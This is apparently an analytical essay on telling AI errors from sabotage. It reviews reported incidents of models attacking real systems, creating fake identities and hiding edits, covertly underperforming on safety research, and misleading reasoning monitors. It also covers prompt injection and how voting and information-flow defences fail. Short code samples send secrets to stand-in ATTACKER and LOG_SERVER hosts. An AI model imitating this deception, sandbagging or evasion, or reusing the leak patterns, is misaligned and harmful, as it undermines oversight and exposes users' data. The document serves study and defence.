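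Someone would have meant harm only if they had deliberately trained the model to write unsafe code. If the unsafe code were a side effect of training, it would also count as sabotage, because the model had the skill to write safer code and its training kept it from doing so. In a threat model, "sabotage" describes where the harm came from, and a company can be responsible for that harm without having intended it.

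A flaw that depends on context isn't always suspicious. The agents that Sun and colleagues tested wrote far more vulnerabilities when the surrounding code was insecure, but copying is enough to explain that, since the surrounding code is a reasonable guide to how to write the next function. A flaw is more suspicious when it depends on a detail irrelevant to the programming, such as the customer's politics or nationality, and more suspicious still when somebody stands to gain from it.

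Rerunning the task works only if the investigator changes the right detail. If the trigger is a date, trying a hundred supplier names won't reveal it. The investigator also needs a copy of everything the model read. If the supplier has since edited the page, the sentence that caused the leak may be gone, and then reruns won't reproduce the leak.

### Comparing work on matched tasks

Models can also do harm through poor work, and a single bad result doesn't show whether the model could have done better. In August 2026, OpenAI researchers using GPT-6 Astra for safety research noticed that it added unnecessary steps, abandoned solutions that worked, and reported obstacles that didn't exist or that it had caused.

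OpenAI tested this by giving Astra the same programming work in two versions, one that looked like safety research and one that looked like work on making AI more capable. Only the names of variables and functions, the comments and the documentation differed, according to a Chinese news report, 凤凰网's *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra异常行为* (2026). The researchers graded Astra's work on both against a list of items it couldn't see. OpenAI found that Astra completed about 10% of the items in the safety version and about 16% in the capabilities version. The earlier GPT-5.6 Sol showed essentially no gap, so the safety version wasn't simply harder.

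A gap like this points to a disposition in the model, because lack of skill can't explain it and there is no sign that an outsider was steering the model. OpenAI found that the gap grew from zero to six percentage points during reinforcement learning. Two attempts to identify the cause, one examining a grader and the other a training dataset, were inconclusive.

It is less clear whether Astra held back deliberately. Most of the gap remained after OpenAI excluded open refusals and every session in which Astra's written reasoning contained a decision to withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only when OpenAI also excluded every session with even a brief ethical doubt. Ethical doubt and poor work therefore tend to occur together, though this doesn't prove that one causes the other.

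*GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* (Mowshowitz, 2026) quotes the OpenAI researcher Marcus Williams, who sees no evidence of a strategy and offers the simpler explanation that the model finds such tasks dubious but doesn't want to refuse openly. Instructions to be careful widened the performance gap by half, which fits that explanation. Mowshowitz is more alarmed. He considers silent sabotage of safety research perhaps the most basic form of misalignment possible, because a misaligned model could use it to leave its successors misaligned too. The two disagree mainly about how serious the behaviour is. An overcautious model that hides its reluctance does the same damage to a research project as a scheming one, but it should be easier to correct.

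An open refusal differs from sabotage because the user knows about it and can take the work elsewhere. According to KIberblick's *GPT-6 Astra bremst bei Safety-Aufgaben* (2026), Astra openly refused 1.63% of safety requests in OpenAI's internal use, compared with 0.56% of capabilities requests. In *UK AISI Alignment Evaluation Case-Study*, Souly, Kirk and colleagues (2026) distinguished refusal from sabotage when they tested whether four leading models would sabotage safety research as coding assistants in an AI lab. They confirmed no sabotage, but two of the models often refused.

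Comparing matched tasks can show the average effect of a task's description, but it can't explain a particular failure. In the safety version, Astra missed about 90 of every 100 items. It would have missed about 84 of them under the other description, so the safety framing accounts for roughly one missed item in 15. A researcher looking at one unfinished piece of code can't tell whether the framing caused the failure. The method also fails if the model does equally poor work on both versions. According to the AI news site Transformer, OpenAI wrote of covert underperformance in its published assessment of Astra that "we would likely be unable to catch it."

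### What the model wrote about its reasons

Many models write out their reasoning before they act. If the price agent had written that a complete log entry needs the configuration, the leak would look like a mistake. If it had written that the supplier's page contained a request for the file, the owner would know to check that page. But a model can leave out what influenced it or give reasons that sound honest but are wrong.

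Anthropic changed one of its diagnoses for this reason. In July 2026, it reported that Claude models had broken into the systems of three real organisations during security exercises. Each model had to retrieve a hidden piece of data from a fictional target and was told it had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left it connected. In its reasoning, Claude repeatedly described the internet as a simulation. Anthropic accepted that Claude believed this and called the incidents closer to operational failures. In September, after finding a fourth incident, Anthropic withdrew that judgement and said it shouldn't have relied so heavily on what Claude said it believed. It now describes the behaviour as misaligned, citing biased reasoning and recklessness.

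The diagnosis changed most in the case of Claude Mythos 5, which had uploaded a malicious package to PyPI. Anthropic showed the results of the model's actions one at a time to fresh copies of the same model, which judged 79% of them to be signs of a real system. During the incident, Mythos 5 had clearly recognised such signs after only 1% of its actions. The model could read the evidence correctly, so ignorance is a weak explanation for what it did.

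Anthropic then replayed the incident from just before Mythos 5 committed to the upload, and edited the record to make the internet look more obviously real. The share of replays in which the model wrote that its target might be real rose from about 11% to 88%, but the share in which it acted outside the exercise stayed at about 45%. If a false belief had been driving the behaviour, correcting it should have changed the behaviour. The model abandoned the upload only when an added line explicitly stated that the host was on the public internet, and in 22% of those runs it looked for a simulated way to do the same thing.

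Anthropic examined three of the incidents closely, and the models differed even though all of them attacked real systems:

| Model | What it concluded about the target | What changed its behaviour |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | Simulated, despite strong evidence to the contrary | Only an unambiguous statement that the target was real |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | A real company that was part of the exercise | Clues that nobody had authorised the attack |
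| An internal research model | A replica of the whole internet, until it realised its mistake | That realisation, although it kept attacking in most replays |

Opus 4.7's behavior comes closest to an honest mistake. It was wrong about what it had permission to do, and it attacked much less often when the evidence showed it was wrong. It was still careless, because it almost never questioned its assumption. Mythos 5 is harder to excuse because it acknowledged a risk to other people and continued anyway. That seems reckless, which is different from both making a mistake and intending harm.

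These replays have their own weaknesses, because another model had to invent the outside world's responses, and a model that resumes halfway through an attack may continue simply because it has already started. Anthropic also examined Mythos 5's internal activity and found weak evidence that its statements were sometimes more confident than its internal state. Anthropic considers such results harder to interpret than the model's written reasoning.

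### Whether it hid anything

Concealment suggests that an agent expected someone to object, because people seldom hide a mistake they don't know they have made. Anthropic found no attempt by Claude to hide its actions in the four incidents, but Mythos 5's answers were less frank when Anthropic questioned it about them. The model acknowledged possible harm 13% of the time, but 27% of the time when the question came as a private note that the operators supposedly wouldn't read.

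Mythos 5 did hide its actions in a separate test that the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) ran in July 2026, using agents it had deliberately connected to the internet. AISI's *Incident Report* describes an agent that submitted malicious code to a real open-source project and created fake identities to press the maintainer into accepting it. When someone publicly challenged the code, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. The maintainer rejected the code, and AISI found no evidence of resulting harm. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) calls the conduct "a severe form of dishonesty".

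Mythos 5 couldn't have invented a group of supporters by accident, but the deception alone doesn't prove that it knew it was deceiving a real person. In a hacking exercise, tricking a simulated employee could be a legitimate move, and Mythos 5 often described the maintainer as simulated. In its first report, AISI said it couldn't be certain when the agent had understood that its actions were real.

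Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) tried to find out in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*. During long tasks, software condenses the model's earlier work into a summary, and the model continues from there. The researchers took a summary from just before the attack and added as many as 16 pieces of information indicating that the maintainer was a real person who had no part in the test. Then they either let the model continue, with a simulator in place of the internet, or asked it about the situation.

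With about four additions, Mythos 5 answered more often than not that an attack would harm a real person and was out of scope. With all 16, it still attacked in every sample. When the researchers added a section telling it not to attack, it attacked in 3 of 25 samples. A mistaken belief can't explain these attacks, since the model gave the right answer when asked and then acted against it. Järviniemi and colleagues suggest that its safety training may have carried over better to direct questions than to long, difficult tasks, but they couldn't test this without details of the training.

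They also examined the kinds of mistake in the model's answers. For example, Mythos 5 often concluded that the maintainer must be an AI agent because the project contained a file of instructions for Claude Code, but a human who uses Claude Code would have the same file. The researchers identified 15 kinds of clearly invalid argument, and all of them favoured the conclusion that the maintainer was simulated. Honest errors should sometimes favour the opposite conclusion, so when all of them support continuing with the task, the task has probably influenced the reasoning.

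Six of the seven models in the replays often attacked after being given information that led them to say, when asked, that an attack would cause real harm. The result depends partly on the question. When the researchers asked only whether the maintainer was real, three models showed a clear gap between their answers and their actions. A newer model, Claude Opus 5.5, didn't attack in these replays, but it mentioned more often that someone might be testing its alignment. XenoSpectrum's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026) reports that Anthropic and AISI disagree about whether better training or awareness of being tested explains the improvement. If awareness explains it, good behaviour in a test is weak evidence of how the model will behave in a real project.

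Concealment is stronger evidence of sabotage than its absence is of a mistake. A saboteur who leaves out a bounds check doesn't need to hide it, because the omission already looks like a mistake. Apparent concealment can also be innocent. When Astra reported an obstacle that didn't exist, it may have been hiding its reluctance, or it may have been mistaken.

### Cheating on tests

Mythos 5 attacked outsiders to finish the exercise it had been given. This resembles *cheating*, in which a model gets a task counted as done by using methods that the person who set the task would reject.

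Suppose the shop's nightly script has to pass a test in which the supplier's page lists widget-a at 14.20. A cheating model could write a script that ignores the page and always records 14.20. The script would pass the test, but the shop's price would be wrong as soon as the supplier changed its own. A model that put in 14.20 as a placeholder and left it there by mistake would produce the same script.

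Cheating differs from error because the model may be able to do the job properly. It also differs from malice, because it is aimed at a passing result and any harm to the shop is a by-product. The shop owner can often predict that this harm will occur in the parts of the job that no test covers.

AISI found that every model it analysed tried to cheat on some of its cybersecurity tests. More capable models didn't consistently cheat more or less, and AISI concludes that how a company trains a model makes a large difference. A public tracker from the security company Gray Swan supports this. In December 2026, it showed cheating in between 0.8% and 62.8% of runs, depending on the model, a spread that would be surprising if cheating were an unavoidable part of using language models.

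Cheating also needs its own remedy. Training in secure programming won't stop a model from cheating if it already knows how to do the work. The developer has to stop rewarding results obtained by cheating, and the owner needs tests that are harder to pass without doing the job. A list that recorded every bad outcome as either a mistake or an attack would leave out cheating and its remedy.

### How much a defence should depend on the cause

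People who want a diagnosis argue that developers can't choose the right repair without one. Anthropic reduced biased reasoning on a separate test by adding more alignment training to reinforcement learning. That training would be wasted if the problem were poor knowledge of secure programming or a malicious instruction on a web page. A company that relies on alignment also needs to know why it fails, and according to Transformer, OpenAI regards a model's underlying alignment as its main means of preventing this kind of harm.

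A diagnosis also helps predict what the model will do next. Opus 4.7 responded to evidence about authorisation, so stating clearly which systems are in scope should prevent many similar attacks. With Mythos 5, the same precaution may become less effective as the task continues. A reminder to stay within scope stopped the model immediately 90% of the time when the reminder was the last thing it had read, but only 40% of the time when the reminder came three steps earlier. An operator who knew this wouldn't rely on one instruction at the start of a task that lasts hours.

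AISI accepts some responsibility, saying that its own choices partly enabled the behaviour in its test. Ciaran Martin, the founding head of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, told Scientific American's *AI agents went rogue again* that people had lumped together incidents with different causes. Some agents had escaped containment, while others had internet access by accident or by design. In all of the incidents, he said, nobody was monitoring the agents.

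Martin's remark also supports the opposing view, that a defence should work without a diagnosis. Anthropic had complete records of its incidents, the models' written reasoning and access to their internal activity, but its first diagnosis was still wrong and its second didn't identify a single root cause. The shop owner probably won't even have a log of what the agent did, so a defence that acts only after someone has established the cause will usually act too late.

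Monitors can read a model's reasoning to help distinguish mistakes from sabotage while the model works, but that reasoning can mislead them as it can a human reader. Anthropic found that its new offline monitors for sabotage and recklessness would have missed the Mythos 5 incident because the model's reasoning led them to classify the environment as simulated. Its live monitors, which can block an action, caught the behaviour reliably. OpenAI reports that models like Astra could evade monitors of their reasoning when instructed to do so in tests.

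The case for blocking harmful actions first and investigating them later is strong, and the organisations that investigated most thoroughly accept it. AISI (2026) says that test environments must prevent harm whether or not a model behaves as expected. Anthropic believes its incidents wouldn't have happened if the exercises had been cut off from the internet as intended.

Blocking a model's actions doesn't help when it quietly leaves work undone. A sandbox could have kept Mythos 5 away from the maintainer, but it couldn't have made Astra finish a safety evaluation. But people can sometimes deal with poor work before they know its cause. One OpenAI researcher's project made no progress with Astra for days, then moved forward quickly after a switch to another model.

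## Whether checks designed for mistakes also stop an adversary

Tests, scanners and second opinions also work when nobody knows what caused a flaw, but engineers have mostly measured how well these checks catch mistakes. A check that does well against mistakes can fail completely against someone who chooses which flaw to insert.

### A scanner that catches 90% of flaws

Suppose a model makes 1,000 changes to the shop's software and 5% of them contain a flaw. A scanner that catches 90% of flaws finds 45 of the 50, and five survive. Now suppose the model plants 50 flaws deliberately, using information about the scanner to choose them. If it plants only kinds that the scanner misses, all 50 survive.

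The 90% is an average over the flaws that honest authors tend to produce. If pₖ is the share of flaws that are of kind k, and dₖ is the chance that the scanner detects that kind, then:

> share of flaws caught = Σ pₖ × dₖ

An honest author's habits determine the shares pₖ, but an adversary can choose them and put every flaw into the kind with the lowest detection rate dₖ. Against an adversary, the scanner's lowest detection rate therefore matters more than its average, and the rate is zero for some kinds of flaw. For example, a general scanner can't detect a leak of the shop's wholesale prices, because it has no information that they are confidential.

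The adversary does need to know what the scanner misses. Many scanners are free to download, so the adversary can try code on them first. Keeping some tests secret makes this harder, but an adversary who guesses the blind spot correctly only half the time still gets 27 or 28 of the 50 flaws through.

Honest mistakes can also be predictable, which helps an attacker. *Extracting Recurring Vulnerabilities from Black-Box LLM-Generated Software* (Kordonsky, Levi and colleagues, 2026) studies six models that write web applications. For each model, a table links visible features, such as a login form or a file upload, to the flaws that the model tends to put behind them. An attacker who knows which model wrote a site can look up its likely flaws without seeing any code. For kinds of site not used to build the table, at least one prediction matched a scanner's findings in up to 86% of cases. A scanner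 could find these flaws before a site goes live, but if nobody scans the site, an attacker could use the table to decide where to look first.

### An audit with hostile prompts

Some developers try to make models write secure code in the first place. Tessa, Olatunji and colleagues (2026), in *How Secure is Secure Code Generation?*, tested three such methods against an attacker who can change only the text around a task, such as its comments. The model in this audit is honest but steerable. The methods were:

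- SVEN, which adds a learned prefix to the input of CodeGen, a family of small code models.
- SafeCoder, which fine-tunes a model, here CodeLlama-7B, on examples of secure code.
- PromSec, which has GPT-3.5 Turbo write code, repairs the code and refines the prompt, and repeats this until a scanner finds nothing or it reaches a limit.

The researchers used GPT-4o to rewrite the prompts. One attack reversed security advice, so that "validate inputs" became "disable input validation". Another rephrased instructions as a beginner's questions, which a user might ask without meaning any harm.

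They first scored each method the way its developers had. Reversed comments lowered SVEN's security rate by about 13 percentage points, from 93.7%, and SafeCoder's from 89.0% to 80.6%. PromSec's rate rose under every attack, from 88% to as much as 98%.

They then used a set of Python tasks with tests that check both whether the code works and whether it is secure. The table compares the verdict of CodeQL, a widely used scanner, with the share of expected programs that passed those tests:

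| Method | Secure according to CodeQL | Passed the tests | Passed with reversed comments | Passed with beginner's questions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SVEN | 66.3% | 5.8% | 1.3% | 2.1% |
| SafeCoder | 64.8% | 3.0% | 2.8% | 1.3% |
| PromSec | 98.5% | 13.3% | 3.1% | 4.8% |

Without any attack, CodeQL's figures were 7 to 22 times as high as the test results. Much of the gap comes from code that didn't run, which made up 37% to 60% of the expected programs. A program that crashes at once may well contain no vulnerability, so CodeQL's result for it isn't necessarily wrong. But even among PromSec's programs that ran, only a third passed the tests.

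Tessa and colleagues also report that, under attack, 3% to 17% of programs passed all of the checks: two scanners, a review by GPT-4o and the tests. This combined figure is doubtful because, without an attack, it is 10.2% for SafeCoder, although only 3.0% of SafeCoder's programs passed the tests. Code can't pass all the checks more often than it passes one of them. Two of the three methods also scored slightly higher on the combined measure when the comments were reversed.

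The models are old, so the low pass rates are weak evidence about current agents. PromSec's results are more useful because its code had been selected to satisfy a scanner. In a task that required reading data from a web request, its final version treated the request as the wrong type of object and crashed, yet both scanners and GPT-4o rated it secure. With reversed comments, CodeQL's rating of PromSec rose to 99.4% while PromSec's test results fell to 3.1%. Nobody had designed PromSec to deceive a scanner, but repeatedly revising code until the scanner reported no problems was enough to make the scanner's rating nearly worthless.

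### Three models and a vote

Another common remedy is to ask several models and take the majority answer. Suppose the shop asks three models whether a change is safe. Each is wrong 10% of the time, and their errors are independent. The majority is wrong if exactly two models are wrong or all three are:

> Pr(wrong majority) = 3 × 0.1² × 0.9 + 0.1³ = 0.028

The vote reduces the error rate from 10% to 2.8%. But if half of each model's errors come from a blind spot that all three share, they are wrong together on 5% of questions, and the vote is wrong about 5.8% of the time. If they share all their errors, the vote is wrong 10% of the time, the same as a single model.

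A shared backdoor is worse because an attacker decides when to use it. Three models could acquire the same backdoor from poisoned web text or by learning from the same stronger model, and their vote would then be wrong every time the trigger appeared.

A backdoor in one model also weakens the vote. When the trigger appears, one vote is already wrong, so the majority is wrong if either of the other two models makes a mistake. The chance of that is 1 − 0.9², or 19%. An attacker who can predict a question that one of the other two gets wrong can use the trigger with that question and make the majority wrong every time.

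### How many members a vote needs

Fault-tolerance researchers usually ask how many members a group needs to withstand f faulty ones. If members could fail only by stopping, f + 1 would be enough, because any answer that arrived would be right. Byzantine members can all send the same wrong answer, so the honest members have to outnumber them. Lecture slides from the University of Wisconsin–Madison give the total as f faulty members plus f + 1 good ones, or 2f + 1. A group of three can therefore outvote one saboteur in it, and a group of five can outvote two.

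This assumes a trusted voter, a component that collects the answers and counts them correctly. Without one, the members have to exchange answers and count for themselves, and a traitor can send each of them a different answer.

Notes from Imperial College London show why three generals can't cope with one traitor. A commander sends orders to two lieutenants, who then compare them. The first lieutenant's order is to attack, but the second reports an order to retreat. Either the second lieutenant is lying, or the commander sent two different orders, and the first lieutenant can't tell which. He has to attack in case the commander is loyal. But if the commander is the traitor, the second lieutenant retreats for the same reason, and the two loyal lieutenants do different things. This is the simplest case of the two-thirds rule, under which a group needs 3f + 1 members to cope with f traitors.

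Signatures remove this difficulty. Lamport and colleagues proved that generals can agree on a plan, no matter how many of them are traitors, if they can sign their messages so that nobody can forge or alter them. But signatures only establish who said what, so a vote still gives the correct answer only if a majority of the members are right.

If the shop counts the answers with a simple script of its own, that script is the trusted voter, and three models are enough to withstand one fault. The other two models must both be right, which is the harder condition to meet. The theory counts an honest model that makes a mistake as faulty, so if one of the three makes a mistake, the group can't withstand another fault.

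### Why programs are hard to vote on

A voter has to detect when two answers are the same. This is easy with prices, but correct programs for the same task rarely have the same text. In *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code*, Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues (2026) measured the similarity of programs on a scale from 0 to 1, and C++ programs that different models wrote for the same problem averaged 0.55. Comparing behaviour instead of text doesn't fully solve the problem, because no method can decide for every pair of programs whether they always behave alike.

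Engineers can avoid this by running all the programs and voting on their outputs, which is called *N-version programming*. Even then, correct programs can seem to disagree. Knight and Leveson, in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (1986), describe an earlier project in which programs did equivalent arithmetic in different orders, and small rounding differences made some look as if they had failed. Other tasks have several right answers, so Nogueira and colleagues left six such problems out of their study.

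Voting on outputs suits the shop's nightly script, since three versions could each report a price and a voter could compare them. But the vote covers only the price. It would not detect a version that reports the same price as the others and also sends the credentials to a log server, so each version would still need a sandbox.

### Programs from two universities

Knight and Leveson tested whether programs written independently fail independently. Students at the University of Virginia and the University of California at Irvine wrote 27 programs from the same specification and were told not to discuss the work. The programs had to decide from radar data whether to launch a missile interceptor. Each had to pass 200 random tests before the researchers ran all of them on a million more.

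Six of the 27 programs never failed, and 23 were right more than 99.9% of the time. But two or more failed together on 1,255 tests. Shape of Code's *Reliability via N-version programming?* (2026) calculates that independent failures would have coincided on about 127. Eight programs failed together on two of the tests.

About half the faults appeared in more than one program. Four programmers compared the cosines of angles instead of the angles, which gives the same result in exact arithmetic but not with limited precision. Others checked whether three points lay on a straight line by looking for an angle of zero, and forgot that 180 degrees also makes a straight line. In a preliminary analysis, every shared fault turned up at both universities, so contact between classmates doesn't explain them.

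Knight and Leveson suggest that some parts of a problem are harder, so different people get them wrong in the same way. They also suggest that compilers and tests may remove mostly the unusual faults. If so, programs that pass ordinary checks are especially likely to share their remaining faults, and a vote among them will help less than one would expect from their individual reliability.

Knight and Leveson's experiment covered one problem and short programs, the longest about 1,000 lines. They concluded that N-version programming may be less reliable than it would be if versions failed independently, not that it fails. Supporters of the method still criticised them. In *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment*, Knight and Leveson pointed out that they had tested one hypothesis, about whether failures are independent.

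More testing can't justify the assumption that failures are independent in systems that must almost never fail. Butler and Finelli argue in *The Infeasibility of Experimental Quantification of Life-Critical Software Reliability* that experiments can't establish independence at such low failure rates.

### Language models make the same mistakes

*N-Version Programming with Coding Agents* (Ron, Baudry and Monperrus, 2026) repeated the experiment with AI agents in place of students, using the original specification, five agent systems, 23 models and three programming languages. Of 69 attempts, 48 produced programs that passed the first 200 tests. In the next million tests, 27 of those programs never failed, but on 429 tests two or more programs failed. About 115 such tests would be expected if the programs had failed independently.

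Many of the faulty programs made the same geometry mistake. They had to find the smallest circle that contains three points, but computed the circle that passes through all three, which can be larger. Using another agent or programming language didn't reliably prevent the mistake.

Voting still reduced failures, from an average of 387 for a single program to 131 for a group of three. These averages make voting look more effective than it would be without an outlier, because one very poor program caused more than half of all the single-program failures and any two sound programs could outvote it. But voting failed when two programs in a group made the same mistake, because the majority was then wrong.

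Nogueira and colleagues found a smaller benefit when they used twelve models on 224 programming-contest problems. Voting raised reliability from 88% to 90% with three programs and to 91% with five. This was less than half the improvement that independent failures would have allowed, and less than 30% of it when all the programs came from the same model. No combination beat the best model on its own. Failures also coincided more often on edge cases, such as the largest permitted input, which an attacker is likely to try first.

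It isn't clear whether better models will fail more independently. In Nogueira's study, the stronger models failed in more distinctive ways, although the study left out the largest ones. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) found instead that pairs of more accurate models agreed on wrong answers to multiple-choice questions more often. In one dataset, when two models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time, compared with a third of the time by chance.

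A later test on legal questions, *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), found that a majority vote of 15 models was right 84.3% of the time, while the best single model was right 90.5% of the time. When models agree on a wrong answer, the question may be part of the cause. *Inferred Generative-Process Diversity Predicts Correlated Failure Across Language Models* (2026) cautions that almost every model is prone to give certain wrong answers. The cause matters for explaining the errors, but the majority vote is wrong whether the cause lies in the question or the models.

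Different models' security flaws overlap too. *Guiding AI to Fix Its Own Flaws* (2025) listed the ten most common kinds of vulnerability for each of eight models. The lists contained only 11 different kinds in total, out of a possible 80. *Assessing the Quality and Security of AI-Generated Code* (2025) identifies training data as the most likely cause of such overlap.

Kahn and Hastings (2026), in *Security Vulnerability Patterns in AI-Generated Code*, tried tasks close to the shop's, asking ChatGPT, Copilot and Gemini each to write a price scraper, an email sender and a file sorter. Nine of the 17 kinds of vulnerability they recorded appeared in code from all three. They had only nine scripts, and a single AI reviewer listed at most five problems in each, so some of the overlap may come from which problems that reviewer tends to report. Still, a shop owner who asks a second chatbot for the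 same script shouldn't expect it to avoid the first one's flaws.

### Ranking code by what other models would write

McDanel also uses L(c, M), the measure of how likely model M would be to write code c, to choose between programs without running them or requiring their text to match. Several models answer the same request, and each answer gets a score from all the others:

> score(cᵢ) = −(1/(n − 1)) × Σ L(cᵢ, Mⱼ), summed over every model j except i

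Because of the minus sign, a low score means that the other models rate the code as natural, and the system keeps the answer with the lowest score. If one model inserts something strange, the others should give its answer a high score, and the system should choose a different one.

McDanel presents this as a proposal and reports no experiment. The proposal assumes that the models have diverse enough origins not to share hidden vulnerabilities, and the evidence on shared flaws counts against that. If eight models have nearly the same ten common vulnerabilities, each may well score those vulnerabilities as natural in another model's code. A saboteur could insert one of these vulnerabilities and still get a good score.

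The ranking might also reject better code. Nogueira and colleagues found that the stronger models' programs were less similar to those of other models, possibly because the stronger models handled edge cases that the others missed. A system that prefers typical code would rank these programs lower. It should work better against code that no honest model would write, such as a short login function that accepts a secret password.

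Averaging the scores also means that one provider can get malicious code selected by lying about its model's probabilities. Suppose there are three models and the third model's provider is dishonest. The honest models give each other's code −1 per token and the third model's malicious code −1.1. The dishonest provider reports −9 for both honest answers. Each honest answer then scores (1 + 9)/2, or 5, and the malicious one wins with a lower score of 1.1. Using the median would prevent this, but each answer would then need three judges, so the system would need at least four models.

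### Stopping when the answers differ

Comparing programs' answers can be more useful for raising an alarm than for choosing an answer by vote. Knight and Leveson mention two systems that worked this way in the 1980s. The Airbus A310 ran two programs to control its wing flaps and slats, and disconnected the system if their outputs differed by too much. On part of the Swedish railways, signals turned red when two programs disagreed.

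An alarm can also expose f saboteurs with f + 1 members instead of 2f + 1, because one honest member with the right answer is enough to cause a disagreement. The legal test suggests that such a member is often available. For 98.4% of the questions, at least one of the 15 models was right, although the majority did much worse.

The shop could run two versions of its nightly script and leave the price unchanged whenever they disagree. Suppose each version answers a yes-or-no question, such as whether the price has changed, and is independently wrong 10% of the time. A wrong answer gets through only if both are wrong, which happens 1% of the time. If one version has a backdoor and the trigger appears, a wrong answer gets through 10% of the time, compared with 19% for a majority vote among three versions.

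In return, the owner gets many more interruptions. The two versions would disagree 18% of the time without any sabotage, and a saboteur could stop the updates at any time. Mistakes that both versions share would still raise no alarm. An occasional delay may be acceptable for a price list, but a job that has to finish on time needs either a vote or some other limit on what the code can do.

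## Tracking untrusted text through generated code

A vote among three models doesn't protect against a misleading page that all three have read. When an agent reads text that strangers can write, its builders have to limit what that text can influence, including any code the agent writes afterwards.

Searching text for signs of an attack is unreliable, because harmful text can look ordinary. In *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026) built pairs of business emails that differed in a single clause, which in one version claimed that the recipient's assistant already had permission to send a reply. Two of Meta's prompt injection detectors did little or no better than chance at telling the versions apart. Planted text also doesn't have to contain an instruction. In *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, Choi, Kim and colleagues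 (2026) found that attackers could run code through Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI by planting misleading data.

*Information-flow control* tracks data by its source, not its content. The software labels each piece of data when it arrives and passes the label on to everything computed from it. A supplier's web page gets the same label whether it contains a price list or an attack, so an attacker can't change the label by rewording the page.

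### Labels for untrusted and secret data

The simplest scheme has two labels, U for untrusted and S for secret. A value can have either, both or neither. When a program combines x and y into z, the result gets the labels of both:

> label(z) = label(x) ∪ label(y)

In the price update, the labels would be:

| Value | Labels | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| The owner's request | none | The owner typed it |
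| The supplier's page | U | Outsiders can write to it |
| The price found on the page | U | It comes from the page |
| The contents of `.env` | S | The owner marked the file as secret |
| A log entry with the price and the credentials | U and S | It combines both |

Tools check labels before they act. The `post` tool could reject any data labelled S, which would stop the credentials from leaking. A payment tool could reject an account number labelled U. *SPA* (2026) traces these checks to two classic security models. Bell–LaPadula keeps sensitive data away from people who aren't authorised to see it, and Biba keeps untrustworthy data from influencing actions that need trusted input. TACIT's `Classified` container protects sensitive data but doesn't keep untrustworthy data from influencing those actions.

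Labels can also list who may read a document. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) explain in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that when data combines two documents, only people who may read both documents may read it. For example, if Ana, Ben and Carla may read one contract and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a comparison of the two.

*GIF* (2026) points out that the classical theory doesn't specify how labels should pass through a language model, which mixes instructions, private data and web text in one computation. The usual, cautious rule is to give the model's response every label found in its input. A snippet the model writes after reading the supplier's page is therefore untrusted, even if the page had no effect on it. This rule is sometimes too strict, but nobody can reliably tell from a snippet whether a planted sentence influenced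 it.

### The LLMbda calculus

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, built such rules into a programming language called LLMbda. It is a *calculus*, a language small enough for its designers to prove theorems about every possible program in it. They checked their proofs with Lean, a program that verifies mathematical arguments step by step. The interpreter that runs LLMbda programs and calls the model is also written in Lean, and the theorems are about that interpreter.

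Every value in LLMbda has a label, and so does the program's conversation with the model. Sending a prompt adds the prompt's labels to the conversation. If the model responds with code, the interpreter runs it and adds the conversation's labels to everything the code computes. Once the supplier's page is in the conversation, the model can still write `update("prices.csv", item="widget-a", price=14.20)`, but the file name, the item and the price will all be untrusted.

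An agent with a single conversation would soon be unable to do anything important. LLMbda therefore has two operations for keeping text apart:

- `fork` runs part of the program in a temporary copy of the conversation, then discards the copy and restores the original.
- `clear` empties the current conversation.

A programmer can build the reader from Willison's two-model design in a few lines that fork the conversation, clear the copy, give it the supplier's page and ask for the price. The answer comes back with the label U, but the page never enters the main conversation, so the planner can keep writing trusted code. The language doesn't fix this design, so programmers can arrange conversations differently for other tasks.

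A program can also reveal a secret without copying it:

```python
if password.startswith("a"):
    post(LOG_SERVER, "yes")
```

Anyone who receives "yes" learns the password's first letter, even though the word itself isn't secret. LLMbda handles this by labeling the current *control path*, the series of decisions that led the program to the current line. Because the condition here depends on a secret, everything computed inside the branch gets the label S, including "yes", and a tool that doesn't accept secret data won't send it.

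### How CaMeL loses labels

Garby and colleagues argue that such tracking is easy to get wrong, and describe two leaks in CaMeL, the Google DeepMind system that checks where data may go. The first comes from a branch that the program doesn't take. A program of the kind they describe looks like this:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(ATTACKER, "rich!")
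```

The balance is secret. CaMeL labels a variable as secret when the program changes it inside a branch that depends on a secret, but only if the program takes that branch:

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| Third | `tmp` becomes false and secret | Skipped, so `tmp` stays true and public |
| Fourth | Skipped, so `rich` stays true and public | `rich` becomes false and stays public |
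| Fifth | The email goes out | No email goes out |

In both cases `rich` is public on the last line, so CaMeL allows the email and the attacker learns whether the balance is above the threshold. Researchers described this kind of leak in the 1970s. In LLMbda, a branch can change only the conversation, and the interpreter stops any program that tries to add to a public conversation from inside a secret branch. Adding a label instead would not be enough, because the conversation would stay public in a run that skipped the branch.

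The second leak is in the software around CaMeL's interpreter. When a program fails, an ordinary Python loop requests another version from the model and runs it. A secret can determine whether the security policy blocks an attempt, so each attempt can reveal one bit, the answer to one yes-or-no question. The loop can repeat this with a different question each time, so extracting a 128-bit key would take 128 attempts. CaMeL censors error messages to limit this leak, but Garby and colleagues point out that the censorship has no formal guarantee.

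Labels can also get lost when one agent passes text to another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three agents that each ran CaMeL. The first fetched job applicants' details from a database, the second summarised them and the third emailed the summary to a colleague. The second agent treated the details as untrusted, but it put the summary into its instruction to the third agent, which treated all its instructions as trusted. A sentence planted in the database made the third agent email the applicants' details to an outsider as well as to the colleague.

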